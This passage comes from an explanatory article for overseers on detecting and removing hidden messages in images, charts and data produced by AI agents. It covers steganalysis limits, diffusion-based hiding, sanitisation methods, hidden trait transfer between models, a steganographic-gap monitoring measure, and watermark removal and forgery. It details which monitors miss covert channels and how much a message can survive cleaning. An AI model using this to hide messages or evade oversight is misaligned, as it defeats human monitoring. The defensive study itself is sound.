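*Reliable Deniable Communication* (2013) advises caution about the square root law, because under other assumptions the message can grow in proportion to the cover. Some versions of the law also include a logarithmic factor. By the formula in *A study on the invariance in security whatever the dimension of images* (2023), quadrupling a one-megapixel image would allow about 2.2 times as many hidden bits, instead of twice as many. The study adds that a uniform image hides a message much less securely than a highly textured one. This helps anyone checking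 business charts, because a bar that should be a single shade of blue has no natural noise to conceal stray values, unlike a photograph of gravel.

Short secrets are still a problem. A 40-character access key takes 320 bits, well below the 1,000 bits in the example. Hiding it in the last bits of the colour values in a 1,000 by 1,000 pixel image would change about 160 of the three million values.

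### How steganalysis works

Most steganalysis begins by separating an image's noise from its content, because the content is far stronger than any hidden signal. Software predicts each pixel from its neighbours and keeps only the error. For example, if a pixel's neighbours are 100 and 102, the software predicts 101. The error is 0 if the pixel is 101, and −1 if it has been changed to 100. A single error doesn't reveal a message, but a message changes how often different errors occur and which ones appear side by side.

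The next step is to measure those patterns. Older detectors calculated statistics that researchers had designed by hand and passed them to a classifier. Since about 2015, neural networks have increasingly replaced these detectors. A developer trains the network on ordinary images and on copies that contain hidden messages, and the network learns which patterns distinguish them. Many of these networks still begin with filters that bring out the noise.

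Finally, the detector gives each image a score and raises an alarm if the score is above a threshold chosen by the developer. Suppose 100 of 10,000 test images without hidden messages score above 0.8. A threshold of 0.8 then gives a false-positive rate of 1%. Raising the threshold reduces false alarms but causes the detector to miss more messages.

### The ALASKA2 competition

The ALASKA2 competition, held in 2020 on the data-science site Kaggle, tested how well these detectors worked on a varied set of images. The organisers supplied 75,000 JPEG images with no hidden messages, saved at three levels of quality. They also supplied three altered copies of each image, each made with a different hiding method, for a total of 300,000 training images. Competitors then had to rank 5,000 new images by how likely each was to contain a message.

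The scoring combined the detection rates at every possible false-positive rate and favoured detectors that worked with few false alarms. A perfect detector would score 1, and random guessing would score about 0.59. *ImageNet Pre-trained CNNs for JPEG Steganalysis*, by Yousfi, Butora and colleagues, describes the team's prize-winning entry, which scored 0.944 on the 1,000 images used for the public ranking and 0.932 on the other 4,000. The entry combined several networks first trained to recognise everyday objects in photographs. Nearly all the top competitors used networks of this kind.

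A score of 0.932 doesn't determine how many messages a detector would catch at a given threshold. Yousfi and colleagues report such figures for data from an earlier ALASKA competition, with messages twice the original length. At a false-positive rate of 5%, one of their networks missed between 0.8% and 31.5% of the messages, depending on the hiding method.

They also found that detectors need the image at full resolution. One small network scored 0.935 when its first layer kept every pixel, but only 0.845 when it averaged neighbouring pixels at that stage, because averaging smooths away the noise. An overseer should therefore run steganalysis on the original file, not on the smaller copy that a vision-language model receives.

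The competition was also easier than real use because the training and test messages were hidden with the same three methods and had the same average length. A real overseer rarely knows the method, the message length or where the images without messages come from.

### When the detector meets unfamiliar images

Detectors often fail on images from a source they weren't trained on, a problem known as *cover-source mismatch*. *Detection of Classifier Inconsistencies in Image Steganalysis* (2019) gives examples such as a different camera, resolution or filter. These change the image noise that the detector examines.

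In *Stego Battlefield*, Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested eight detectors against 12 hiding methods on two collections of ordinary images, one of them a sample from ALASKA2. The two best detectors were nearly perfect when the training and test images came from the same collection and the messages were hidden by the same method. They even caught a method that changed colour values by only about one step on average.

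When the researchers tested the detectors on the other collection, four detectors' F1 scores for one hiding method fell from between 0.97 and 0.99 to between 0.01 and 0.03. F1 scores range from 0 to 1 and combine missed messages with false alarms. A score that low means that a detector misses almost every message. Some methods remained easy to detect on both collections. Detectors could fail just as badly when the hiding method changed. One scored 0.98 on the method it was trained on, but between 0.00 and 0.03 on the other four methods for hiding text.

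A report of "no hidden message found" is therefore worth little unless someone has tested the detector on images like the ones under review.

### Messages in AI-generated images

Hidden messages are harder to detect in AI-generated images because the sender doesn't need to alter an existing picture, so an overseer has no original to compare with the result. Many image generators are *diffusion models*, which start from random noise and gradually turn it into a picture. A sender can use the message to set the starting noise. The recipient then runs the process backwards to recover the noise and reads the message from it.

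Zhu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Rethinking Security of Diffusion-based Generative Steganography*, tested nine methods of hiding messages in images generated by diffusion models. They proved that, if the generation process is exactly reversible, the relative entropy between images with and without hidden messages is the same as between their starting noise. A method can therefore be detected if and only if it changes the distribution of that noise, even slightly. Their detector, NS-DSer, estimates an image's starting noise and calculates ten statistics from it, such as the mean and variance.

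The table compares NS-DSer with UCNet, an older kind of detector that examines the picture itself. Half of the images in each test contained hidden messages, so guessing would be right 50% of the time. In the last two columns, half of the images without messages were photographs.

| Hiding method | UCNet, generated images only | NS-DSer, generated images only | UCNet, photographs added | NS-DSer, photographs added |
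|---|---|---|---|---|
| MC | 92.9% | 99.8% | 90.6% | 99.7% |
| GSD | 49.7% | 99.6% | 73.8% | 99.6% |
| CRoSS | 93.7% | 85.7% | 93.5% | 90.3% |
| Four methods meant to preserve the noise | 50–52% | 50–52% | 73–74% | 62–63% |

Neither detector could find messages from the last four methods when every image was AI-generated. UCNet's accuracy was much higher when photographs were added, but Zhu and colleagues conclude that the detectors had learned to tell photographs from generated images. UCNet was right almost exactly 75% of the time, which is consistent with flagging every generated image. A detector that did this would catch all the messages and clear all the photographs, but wrongly flag the other half of the images without messages. If an overseer used such a detector on an agent that only generates images, it would flag every image.

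NS-DSer did almost as well on the detectable methods when the pictures came from several generators with varying settings, with accuracy between 96% and over 99% for four of them. But all the generators were versions or close relatives of Stable Diffusion, an openly available model that NS-DSer also uses to recover the noise. Its results may not carry over to a commercial generator whose workings are secret. An overseer who has never seen innocent images from that generator doesn't know what its normal noise looks like.

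### Ten messages in a million images

Even a good detector has trouble finding something rare. Suppose a company's agents make one million images, and ten of them contain hidden messages. Suppose also that the detector catches 90% of the images with messages and wrongly flags 1% of the images without them.

| | Images | Alarms |
|---|---|---|
| With a message | 10 | 9 |
| Without a message | 999,990 | About 10,000 |

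Only nine of roughly 10,009 alarms are correct, about one in 1,100. When messages are rare, even a small false-positive rate produces far more false alarms than correct ones, which is known as the *base-rate problem*.

Checking 10,000 alarms is harder than running the detector. The detectors that Sun and colleagues timed mostly took 1.3 to 1.5 milliseconds per image, so a million images would take about 25 minutes. A person can open a picture flagged for written instructions and read them, but a picture flagged by steganalysis will usually look normal whether or not it contains a message. Trying to extract the message doesn't settle the matter either, because an encrypted message looks like random bits without the key.

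For half the alarms to be correct, the false-positive rate would have to be about nine in a million. Demonstrating a rate that low would require testing about 330,000 innocent images without a false alarm. The tests of NS-DSer used 200 innocent images at a time. Even with no false alarms on 200 images, the false-positive rate could be as high as 1.5%, or 15,000 false alarms per million innocent images.

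Routine steganalysis of every image is therefore a poor use of reviewers' time unless messages are much more common than in this example. For routine work, it is often more practical to destroy possible messages in all images without trying to detect them. The scores can still be worth storing in case an agent later comes under suspicion.

### Investigating a suspect agent

The same detector is much more useful when there is already a reason to suspect an agent. Suppose another agent has acted on information it should not have had, and the only known contact between the two was 100 images. If 20 of those images contain messages, the detector will flag about 18 of them and, on average, fewer than one of the other 80, so nearly every alarm will be correct.

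The number of alarms is also evidence. An innocent agent's 100 images would produce one false alarm on average, and five or more only about once in 300 cases. But five alarms are convincing only if the investigator had a separate reason to examine that agent. A company that checked 10,000 innocent agents and accused every one with five or more alarms would wrongly accuse about 34 of them.

The calculation also assumes that false alarms occur independently, and cover-source mismatch can easily break this assumption. If the detector wasn't trained on images like those from the agent's generator, it may flag dozens of innocent pictures for the same reason. An investigator can check for this by making several hundred innocent images with the same generator, settings and kinds of request, and running the detector on them. If it flags 20% of them, 20 alarms from the suspect agent are not evidence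 of hidden messages. The investigator can also use the new images to retrain the detector or choose a better threshold.

Analysing a suspect's images together can reveal a trace too weak to find in a single image. Levecque, Noirault and colleagues (2025), in *Targeted Pooled Latent-Space Steganalysis Applied to Generative Steganography, with a Fix*, studied one of the four methods that neither NS-DSer nor UCNet could detect. They noticed that its starting noise always has exactly the same overall strength, while the strength of ordinary noise varies slightly. Recovering the noise from an image blurs this difference, so a test on one image was wrong 48.4% of the time, hardly better than guessing. The error rate fell to 45% with batches of ten images and 34% with batches of 100.

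That is still too unreliable to prove anything by itself. Each batch also contained either only innocent images or only images with messages, so a suspect who hid messages in just a few of 100 pictures would be harder to catch. The researchers then showed that randomly varying the strength of the noise removes the trace, after which their test did no better than chance.

An investigator should also look at how the agent made its images. An agent that edits pixels with code will usually leave that code in the record of its work, and there are few innocent reasons for a program to change the least significant bits of the pixels in a finished chart. A network like CycleGAN would leave no such record, because it learned to hide the information during training. The investigator would instead have to alter the images slightly and check whether the receiving model loses information that it should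 never have had.

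## Removing hidden messages without finding them

The slight changes that would expose a hidden message in one of CycleGAN's maps would also destroy the message. An overseer can therefore make such changes to every image an agent produces, without first testing any of them. This form of sanitisation produces no false alarms because it doesn't flag images, but it also alters images that contain no hidden message. The changes must be strong enough to destroy a message but mild enough to leave the image usable.

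Robinette, Moyer and Johnson measured both sides of this trade-off in *Sanitizing Hidden Information with Diffusion Models* (2023). Their method, DM-SUDS, uses a diffusion model to clean an existing picture rather than generate a new one.

### How DM-SUDS cleans an image

The software first adds random noise to the image:

noisy image = √a × original image + √(1 − a) × random noise

The number *a* starts near 1 and falls towards 0 as the software moves to higher noise settings. If *a* is 0.96, the software multiplies the original by about 0.98 and the noise by 0.2, which typically shifts a colour value by about 25 steps on the scale from 0 to 255. A hidden change of one step is lost among shifts of that size.

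The diffusion model then estimates the noise, and the software subtracts it. The model has learned from many ordinary pictures what a clean one looks like, so it can restore an edge or a patch of sky from the surrounding pixels. This training doesn't help it restore a faint hidden pattern.

Robinette and colleagues used a publicly available diffusion model without training it on any hidden messages. Their method therefore doesn't have to detect how a message was hidden, whereas steganalysis often fails on unfamiliar hiding methods. The added noise matters most. When they skipped it and ran only the denoising step, the hidden content was still recognisable at the highest setting.

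### What the cleaning removed and what it damaged

The researchers hid one picture inside another, the cover, in three ways. The first stored the hidden picture in the cover's least significant bits. The second used a neural network that adapts the hidden picture to its cover ("dependent" hiding), and the third used a network that turns the hidden picture into a pattern that fits any cover ("universal" hiding). They made 1,000 pairs for each method, and the pictures were only 32 by 32 pixels.

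They scored the results by correlation, where 1 means two pictures match perfectly and 0 means they are unrelated. Cleaning succeeded if the cleaned picture had a correlation of at least 0.95 with the original cover and the recovered secret had a correlation of at most 0.30 with the original secret. In each table cell, the first number is for the cover and the second is for the secret.

| Cleaning method | Least significant bits | Dependent hiding | Universal hiding |
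|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0.99 / 1.00 | 0.98 / 0.98 | 0.99 / 0.97 |
| Random noise on the pixels | 0.92 / 0.02 | 0.90 / 0.50 | 0.92 / 0.39 |
| Random noise on the picture's frequencies | 0.95 / 0.02 | 0.93 / 0.83 | 0.95 / 0.82 |
| SUDS, the group's earlier method | 0.93 / 0.00 | 0.92 / 0.24 | 0.94 / 0.04 |
| DM-SUDS | 0.97 / 0.01 | 0.95 / 0.25 | 0.97 / 0.04 |

Every removal method destroyed secrets hidden in the least significant bits. Adding plain noise left much of the secret intact when a neural network had hidden it, and damaged the cover more than DM-SUDS did. Only DM-SUDS met both criteria for all three hiding methods.

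The cleaning method narrowly passed one later test, which used pictures of 128 by 128 pixels and PRIS, a hiding method designed to survive JPEG compression. After cleaning, the secret had a correlation of 0.30, exactly the limit.

The amount of noise determines the balance between removing the secret and preserving the cover image. At a setting of 25, a boat in one of the hidden pictures was still visible after cleaning. At 1,000, cleaning removed the secret but blurred the cover. Fewer than half of the 40 settings met both criteria. The main results come from a setting of 500.

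These tests used photographs, and cleaning may damage charts more. In the main test, cleaned colour values typically differed from the original by 12 to 15 steps. That is hard to notice in a photograph, but it could make a solid blue bar look blotchy. A model trained on photographs might also restore a blurred 3 as an 8, which would barely change the correlation for the whole picture. An overseer who cleans charts this way should run OCR before and after and compare the numbers.

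Speed is another obstacle. Cleaning took about 0.1 seconds for the smallest pictures and about two seconds for those of 128 by 128 pixels. If the time keeps growing in proportion to the number of pixels, a chart of 1,000 by 1,000 pixels would take about two minutes.

Correlation is also a poor measure for a hidden password, because the number of bits that survive is what matters. The closest evidence comes from audio. Robinette and colleagues hid sentences from Shakespeare's *Twelfth Night* in 250 audio clips, then cleaned the clips with a diffusion model for music. Afterwards, between 44% and 49% of the recovered bits were wrong, depending on the hiding method, compared with the 50% expected from guessing.

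The small difference between 44% and 50% still leaves room for a message. If a share *p* of the bits is wrong and the errors are independent, each stored bit can convey at most this much information:

1 + p log₂ p + (1 − p) log₂(1 − p)

For the highest survival rate in the audio test (*p* = 0.4365), the result is about 0.012 bits. Even with efficient error correction, a sender would need at least 27,000 stored bits, instead of 320, to get a 40-character access key through. A chart with three million colour values has room for that, although cleaning an image might cause more errors than cleaning a sound clip did. Cleaning therefore greatly reduces the length of message that can get through, but a sender who expects it may still get a short one past.

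### Compression, noise and resizing at a security gateway

A *security gateway* checks files as they enter or leave an organisation's network. *Training-Free Color-Aware Adversarial Diffusion Sanitization for Diffusion Stegomalware Defense at Security Gateways* (Frants and Agaian, December 2025) compares several ways a gateway could clean every image. The target is Pulsar, which hides a message in the random choices a diffusion model makes while generating a picture. Pulsar encodes the message with an error-correcting code so that it can survive some damage.

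The paper's own method, ADS, first adds a little noise to the picture. It then calculates which tiny change would most disrupt a diffusion model's attempt to reconstruct the picture, applies that change, and removes the noise in a single step. One version adjusts red, green and blue separately, while another adjusts them together to avoid coloured speckles.

The table gives results for 64 images of 256 by 256 pixels. Visible change is measured by LPIPS, which uses a neural network to estimate how different two pictures look to a person, with zero meaning no difference.

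| Cleaning method | Messages lost | Visible change | Time per image |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1.6% | 0 | 0.3 ms |
| JPEG, quality 90 | 89.1% | 0.0028 | 1.8 ms |
| JPEG, quality 70 | 100% | 0.0126 | 1.7 ms |
| Shrinking to 224 pixels and enlarging again | 59.4% | 0.0647 | 2.0 ms |
| Mild blur | 12.5% | 0.0329 | 2.1 ms |
| Strong blur | 100% | 0.2606 | 2.1 ms |
| One plain diffusion step | 7.8% | 0.0008 | 27.7 ms |
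| ADS, colours separate | 100% | 0.0048 | 82.8 ms |
| ADS, colours together | 98.4% | 0.0022 | 82.9 ms |

Resizing changed the picture more than light JPEG compression did and destroyed fewer messages. The plain diffusion step did little, which fits Robinette and colleagues' finding that too little noise leaves the hidden message in place.

The percentages of lost messages can rank the cleaning methods, but they don't show how much of a message a recipient could read. Frants and Agaian counted a message as recovered if at most 48% of its bits were wrong, because this limit matched the cases in which Pulsar's error correction succeeded. After a mild blur, an average of 47.1% of the bits were wrong, yet the table shows only 12.5% of messages as lost. Even in untouched images, 28.8% of the bits were wrong.

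ADS also benefited from using the same diffusion model that had generated the pictures, an advantage a real gateway would rarely have. It might do worse against a sender who used a different model. With only 64 images, even a perfect score is compatible with up to about 4.6% of messages surviving.

For most organisations, JPEG compression at quality 70 is probably the better place to start. It destroyed every message in the test, takes about a fiftieth of the time and needs no graphics processor. Its main drawback for charts is that it leaves faint smudges around letters and sharp edges.

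JPEG compression alone isn't enough against a sender who prepares for it. PRIS is designed to hide content that survives compression, and Agent Smith's picture still spread widely when its designers prepared it for resizing and compression. Frants and Agaian suggest that randomly varying the cleaning and rotating between models may help, since the sender can't then design the image for one known treatment. Cleaning can also damage watermarks that show where an image came from.

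### Messages in what the picture shows

Successful cleaning preserves whatever a viewer can see, so it doesn't remove visible messages. The instructions in the Ghostcommit image would still be legible after cleaning, as would a customer's name on a chart's bar. Signals that look like ordinary design choices would also remain. If two agents had agreed that a blue title means "go ahead" and a grey one means "wait", the colour would survive every method in the table.

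*How does Fable 5.1 hide messages in images?* (Kezin, 13ryanC and colleagues, 2026) describes an October 2026 experiment. In it, frontier models recovered 78% and 88% of the messages hidden in images, according to Al Watan's *رسائل سرية بالذكاء الاصطناعي* (2026).

Stronger cleaning doesn't solve this problem. To remove a signal from the title's colour, the software would have to change the colour, but it can't identify which visible features carry signals. Changing every visible feature would make the chart useless.

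### Redrawing a chart from approved data

Redrawing a chart is better than cleaning it. The overseer discards the agent's picture and keeps only the table of numbers behind it. Once someone has approved the table, a separate program draws the chart from a fixed template. As with rebuilding an office file, the new version contains only what the overseer has allowed.

The template takes away the agent's choice of colours, fonts, spacing and bar order. An agent that can choose among 16 equally acceptable designs can hide four bits (log₂ 16) in each chart, so 80 charts could convey a 40-character access key. With only one possible design, the choice of design conveys no bits. The template also keeps text sharp, whereas JPEG compression or a diffusion model may blur it.

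An agent can still hide a message in the numbers. If it can change the last three digits of a sales total without anyone noticing, it can choose among 1,000 values, which is enough to encode about ten bits. Four regional totals would give it about 40 bits. Rounding to the nearest thousand removes nearly all of this capacity. Recalculating the totals from the original records with ordinary software is safer still, because it gives the agent no choice of values and also catches honest mistakes.

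Words need similar treatment. The program can take region names from a fixed list, but a title or footnote written by the agent could still contain a message or an embedded instruction, so the overseer would have to read it or leave it out.

Redrawing needs structured data, so it works for a bar chart but not for a photograph or a screenshot. It also loses useful details that the template has no place for, such as an arrow marking the month a factory closed. And it doesn't remove data that readers shouldn't see, so a bar that stands for a single customer reveals as much as before. An organisation that makes the same kinds of chart every month should probably redraw them, and keep pixel cleaning for pictures with no underlying data table.

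### Number sequences that passed on a preference

A person who approves a table by looking at it can also miss signals that would affect a model later trained on that table. Cloud, Le and colleagues (2026) found in *Language models transmit behavioural traits through hidden signals in data* that plain numbers can pass a preference from one model to another, even though the numbers have no apparent connection to that preference.

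In the main experiment, the researchers told a "teacher" model, GPT-4.1 nano, that it loved owls and had it continue 30,000 sequences of numbers. A filter removed every answer that wasn't in the required format, leaving only digits, spaces and basic punctuation. The researchers then used 10,000 of the remaining answers to train a "student", another copy of GPT-4.1 nano without the instruction about owls.

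When asked for its favourite animal in 50 different wordings, the student named the owl more than 60% of the time, compared with 12% before training. The same thing happened, to varying degrees, with all ten animals and trees in the experiment. Students trained on numbers from a teacher with no stated preference showed no comparable change, so the format of the data wasn't the cause.

Harmful tendencies also passed from teacher to student through numbers. The researchers trained a GPT-4.1 teacher on insecure computer code, which made it give harmful answers to unrelated questions. They then trained a student on numbers the teacher generated, after removing those with bad associations, such as 666. The student still gave harmful answers to almost 10% of neutral questions, compared with less than 1% for students of teachers that didn't give harmful answers.

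A student usually picked up the teacher's preference only if both had started from the same base model. The exception was GPT-4.1 and GPT-4o, which influenced each other and reportedly share a starting point. This suggests the numbers did not contain a coded reference to owls, because other models should have been able to learn that too.

Cloud and colleagues also proved a theorem that helps explain this. If a teacher and a student start with identical settings and the teacher changes slightly, a small training step towards the teacher's outputs can't move the student away from the teacher and will almost always move it closer. This is true whatever the outputs are about, and as with CycleGAN, nobody has to intend the transfer.

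GPT-4.1 nano's preferences stayed the same when the researchers put the numbers in its prompt instead of training it on them. This risk therefore arises when a company saves its agents' files and trains the next version of the same model on them, not when a downstream agent opens a spreadsheet to summarise it.

The filter failed because it looked for suspicious content, and each sequence looked innocent. Recalculating the numbers would help with sales totals, since an agent can't leave a pattern in numbers it doesn't choose. It can't help with data that an agent invents, such as sample customers for testing a program. For those files, a company would have to record which model made them and avoid using them to train a related model. Cloud and colleagues similarly recommend that safety checks cover where models and training data come from. They note that their prompts were much simpler than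 real uses, and that in some open-weight models preferences for certain animals didn't transfer at all.

### The steganographic gap

An overseer who can't see anything wrong with an artifact can still examine what it does for its recipient. Anwar, Piskorz and colleagues (2026), in *A Decision-Theoretic Formalisation of Steganography With Applications to LLM Monitoring*, base a measure on this idea, the *steganographic gap*. It compares a receiver suspected of knowing the code with a *sentinel*, a trusted model of similar ability that doesn't know it:

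gap = (R₁ − R₀) − (S₁ − S₀)

R₁ is the receiver's best score on some task with the signal, and R₀ is its best score without it. S₁ and S₀ are the same scores for the sentinel. Suppose a receiver has to predict which of two companies will win a contract. It is right 50% of the time without an agent's chart and 90% of the time with it. The chart raises the sentinel's score only from 50% to 60%. The gap is the receiver's gain of 40 percentage points minus the sentinel's gain of 10, or 30 points. Dividing this by the receiver's gain gives a normalised gap of 0.75, meaning three quarters of the chart's usefulness was available only to the receiver.

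Unlike detectors, the measure works without examples of innocent images, which an overseer often lacks. In principle, it can even reveal a message that no statistical test of the image could detect.

Anwar and colleagues' main experiments all used text, not images. In one, they trained models to use code words while tracking a coin through a series of flips. The written reasoning raised the receiver's accuracy by 52 percentage points. A sentinel that knew half of the code words gained 37 points, for a normalised gap of 0.29. The gap was 0.92 with a sentinel that knew none.

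In a different experiment, researchers trained a small model to rewrite the coded reasoning so that the sentinel could use it too, without changing the receiver's answers. This nearly eliminated the gap between the sentinel and the receiver. Unlike pixel cleaning, which destroys a message, this kind of cleaning keeps its useful content.

The result depends heavily on the task, so an overseer who chooses the wrong one can miss the message. When the researchers encoded the words in a piece of mathematical reasoning but left the numbers alone, the gap was close to zero for solving the problem but large for detecting remarks that showed the model knew it was being tested. A receiver could also hide its advantage by deliberately doing badly, or by using the information only after the test. The measure would probably also miss Cloud and colleagues' number sequences, because they had no effect on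 a model that only read them.

A gap can appear just because the sentinel is less capable than the receiver. Applying the measure to images would make this problem worse, because models differ widely in how well they read small labels and crowded charts. Anwar and colleagues recommend comparing several sentinels. For a chart, the overseer could also give every model the approved table of numbers along with the picture. If the receiver still gains more from the picture than the sentinels do, misread labels are a less likely explanation.

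## SynthID and other image watermarks

Cleaning an image can also destroy a hidden signal that belongs there, such as SynthID, the invisible watermark Google adds to images its AI products generate. If a detector finds the watermark, an AI tool from Google or one of its partners probably made or edited the image. The watermark doesn't indicate whether the image leaks data or contains instructions for another agent.

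### How SynthID marks an image

*SynthID-Image* (Gowal, Bunel and colleagues, Google DeepMind, 2025) describes the two neural networks that SynthID uses. The *encoder* takes a finished picture and returns an almost identical copy that contains the watermark. The *decoder* takes any picture and returns a score, which is high if the watermark seems to be there.

The researchers train the encoder and decoder together. Software randomly edits marked and unmarked pictures, for example by cropping or compressing them, and the decoder has to identify the marked ones. A limit on visible change stops the encoder from using an obvious mark.

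The encoder can also add a *payload*, a short message that could identify, for instance, which partner's tool made the picture. SynthID-O, the version Google offers to partners, fits 136 bits into a 512 by 512 pixel picture. A longer payload is harder to recover after editing, and a stronger mark is easier to see, so the designers have to compromise.

Because the encoder works on finished pictures, Google can use it with any image generator. Plain pictures, such as logos with a few flat colours or nearly uniform images, are the hardest to mark invisibly. Gowal and colleagues note that a system can leave such pictures unmarked. Many business charts also have large areas of a single colour. Agents usually draw charts with code instead of an image generator, so the charts presumably never pass through the encoder.

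### How well the mark survives editing

Gowal and colleagues tested SynthID-O and several published watermarks on 10,000 photographs with 30 kinds of everyday edit, such as rotation, compression and added text. They set each detector to wrongly flag an average of 0.1% of unmarked pictures when the edits were at full strength. The table lists some of the detectors and the share of marked pictures each one found.

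| Watermark | Edits of random strength | Edits at full strength |
|---|---|---|
| SynthID-O | 99.98% | 99.72% |
| WAM | 90.6% | 83.4% |
| VideoSeal 1.0 | 88.8% | 76.8% |
| StegaStamp | 72.5% | 66.7% |
| InvisMark | 70.2% | 60.3% |

SynthID-O's weakest result was 98.06%, when several full-strength edits were combined. In a separate study, people looked for visible flaws in 1,000 generated pictures, and SynthID-O added fewer than any of the other watermarks.

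Google ran these tests on its own product. The test images were photographs, so the rates may not apply to charts. Google hasn't published accuracy rates for its public detector.

### Who uses SynthID and who can check for it

OpenAI has added SynthID watermarks to images generated through ChatGPT, Codex and its API since May 2026, according to its *Advancing content provenance for a safer, more transparent AI ecosystem* (2026). Google DeepMind's *Google SynthID* also names Nvidia and Kakao as partners, with Apple to follow soon. Google says 180 billion images and videos now carry SynthID watermarks (gen-ai.news, 2026).

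In October 2026, Google opened its SynthID Detector website, previously limited to testers, to anyone who signs in. Rijo (2026), in *Google's SynthID Detector gains public access and covers 4 companies*, reports that the site has daily limits and that its terms forbid bulk checking by software. So an overseer can use it to check a single suspicious picture, but not everything an agent makes.

Two other services accept requests from software. Google Cloud offers businesses a detection service that also looks for signs of other popular models, according to InfoQ (2026). OpenAI's *Content provenance* describes a service that finds only OpenAI's signals and has strict rate limits, though organisations can apply for higher ones. The limits make it harder to remove a watermark by repeatedly editing a picture and checking whether the detector still finds the mark.

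Checking a confidential picture this way requires sending it to another company. Google's website deletes each upload after giving the result but keeps a fingerprint of it for 24 hours. OpenAI's zero-retention option doesn't cover these checks. An overseer who uploads a customer's billing screen to find out where it came from may break the confidentiality rule the check was meant to enforce.

### Marks built into the image generator

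Stable Signature builds the watermark into the image generator. It works with generators that first create a compressed version of the picture and then use a final network to turn it into pixels. Fernandez, Couairon and colleagues (2023), in *The Stable Signature*, retrain that final network so that every picture it produces contains the same string of bits, which a separate network can then read.

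This design suits models that anyone can download. Users of Stable Diffusion, one such model, could switch off its original watermark by changing one line of code, because the program added the mark in a separate step. Stable Signature has no separate step to switch off. However, each new string needs a newly trained network. *METR* (2024), a watermarking paper unrelated to the evaluation group of that name, describes this as unworkable for a service that wants a different mark for each of millions of users.

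Tree-Ring, another design from 2023, puts a pattern of rings into the random noise from which a diffusion model starts. To find the rings, a detector has to recover that noise from the picture. Gowal and colleagues point out that this takes a lot of computation, which is a problem because they expect companies to check pictures far more often than they mark them. The rings also change the distribution of the noise, and Zhu and colleagues' theorem implies that a good enough test could detect such a change without knowing the pattern.

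A later design avoids this weakness with *pseudorandom codes*, which Christ and Gunn (2024) introduced in *Pseudorandom Error-Correcting Codes*. The software uses a secret key to turn a message into a long string that determines the starting noise and looks random to anyone without the key. Someone with the key can estimate the noise from the finished picture and decode the message, even if some of the recovered string is wrong.

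The watermark in *An Undetectable Watermark for Generative Image Models* (Gunn, Zhao and Song, 2024) is undetectable in the sense that no efficient program without the key can tell marked pictures from unmarked ones, even after requesting many examples. This is a weaker guarantee than Wang and Moulin's perfect security, because the two kinds of picture differ statistically, though finding the difference should take an impractical amount of computing. The guarantee depends on the watermark's error-correcting code being hard to break, and cryptographers have begun to look for weaknesses in such codes, as in *Cryptanalysis of LDPC-Based Pseudorandom Error-Correcting Codes* (2025).

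### How many bits have to match

Suppose a company's mark is a string of 48 bits. Editing the image can change some of them, so the detector shouldn't require all 48 to match. It could report the mark if at least 41 do.

An unmarked picture can pass this test by luck. If it matches each bit with probability one half, as in 48 coin flips, the chance of at least 41 matches is:

(C(48,41) + C(48,42) + … + C(48,48)) / 2⁴⁸ = 87,825,941 / 281,474,976,710,656 ≈ 0.00000031

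C(48,41) is the number of ways to choose which 41 bits match. The false-positive rate is therefore about 3 in 10 million.

A stricter test raises fewer false alarms but misses more marked pictures. The table shows this for pictures with an average of 90% or 80% of their bits still correct after editing, assuming independent errors.

| Matches required | Unmarked pictures flagged | Marked pictures found, 90% of bits correct | Marked pictures found, 80% of bits correct |
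|---|---|---|---|
| 36 of 48 | 3.6 in 10,000 | 99.9% | 85% |
| 41 of 48 | 3.1 in 10 million | 90% | 23% |
| 44 of 48 | 7.6 in 10 billion | 47% | 2.5% |

Comparing a picture with many different marks also raises the false-positive rate. If a company gives each of its 1,000 agents a different mark and requires 41 matching bits, about 3 in 10,000 unmarked pictures will match at least one mark. With a million users, each with a different mark, the rate rises to about 27%, so a service of that size needs a longer mark or a stricter test.

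The calculation assumes that the bits behave like fair coin flips, but Gowal and colleagues note that they usually don't. A network that reads the bits may be biased towards certain values even in unmarked pictures. If each bit read from an unmarked picture had a 60% chance of matching, about 1.3 in 10,000 such pictures would reach 41 matches, roughly 400 times as many as with fair coin flips.

Gowal and colleagues recommend comparing the picture's score with the scores of real unmarked pictures:

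p = (1 + unmarked pictures that score at least as high) / (1 + all unmarked pictures)

If none of 9,999 unmarked pictures scores as high as the new one, p is 1 in 10,000. A detector that reports a mark only when p is at most 0.001 has a false-positive rate of at most 0.1%, provided that the comparison pictures resemble the ones it checks. Reaching a false-positive rate of 3 in 10 million would take more than three million unmarked pictures.

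### Removal and forgery

Watermarks survive everyday edits more easily than deliberate attempts to remove them. In the NeurIPS 2024 competition "Erasing the Invisible", entrants had to remove watermarks while preserving image quality, and could submit attempts for scoring only five times a day, according to *First-Place Solution to NeurIPS 2024 Invisible Watermark Removal Challenge* (2025). *Watermark Overwriting Attack on StegaStamp algorithm* (2025) reports that the fifth-place entry, out of 65 participants, removed the watermarks from all 150 test images with little loss of quality.

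StegaStamp did very well on some of the everyday edits in Google's test. Its detector found every mark after noise was added, even at full strength. People also rated StegaStamp the most visible of the watermarks compared. A watermark can therefore be visible and survive some ordinary edits perfectly, but still fail against someone who studies it.

These results don't show how easily someone could remove SynthID. The EBU, an association of public broadcasters, mentions online tools advertised as able to remove it, but gives no success rates. Google's published results cover everyday edits, not deliberate attacks. Gowal and colleagues consider perfect security impossible and aim to make large-scale attacks by outsiders too expensive. Gunn and colleagues report that the removal attacks available in 2024 couldn't remove their pseudorandom-code watermark without significantly damaging the pictures,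 though newer attacks may do better.

*Forgery* puts a genuine-looking mark on a picture that the tool never made. It could make a real photograph look AI-generated, or make an outsider's picture look like the work of a company's own agent. Overseers should therefore run the other checks on marked pictures too.

Google trains SynthID to make each mark depend on the picture's content, so that a mark copied onto another picture is less likely to work. Gowal and colleagues also suggest keeping fingerprints of generated pictures and accepting a mark only if the picture matches one of them. They don't report how often forgery succeeds against either measure. *CSGuard* (2026) proposes a diffusion-model watermark meant to resist forgery.

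A cryptographic signature inside the mark would stop outsiders from forging a new message, but it needs a lot of space. Guan and colleagues propose marking each picture with a signed identifier of the user who requested it. Their signatures are 1,024 bits long, while SynthID-O's payload holds 136 bits.

### Signed metadata and how it gets lost

*C2PA* is an industry standard for recording a picture's origin in its metadata. The program that makes the picture writes a statement with details such as its own name, the time and any edits. It adds a fingerprint of the picture and signs both with a private key. Other software can check the signature, and the check fails if anyone has altered the statement or the picture without the key.

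C2PA metadata can contain much more detail than a watermark, but it's easier to lose. OpenAI warns that uploading, resizing or converting a file can remove or break it. A screenshot is a new file, so it has none of the original's metadata. Guan and colleagues add that users can strip the metadata on purpose. Some of the checks described earlier rebuild a file to remove hidden data, which can also discard the signed metadata.

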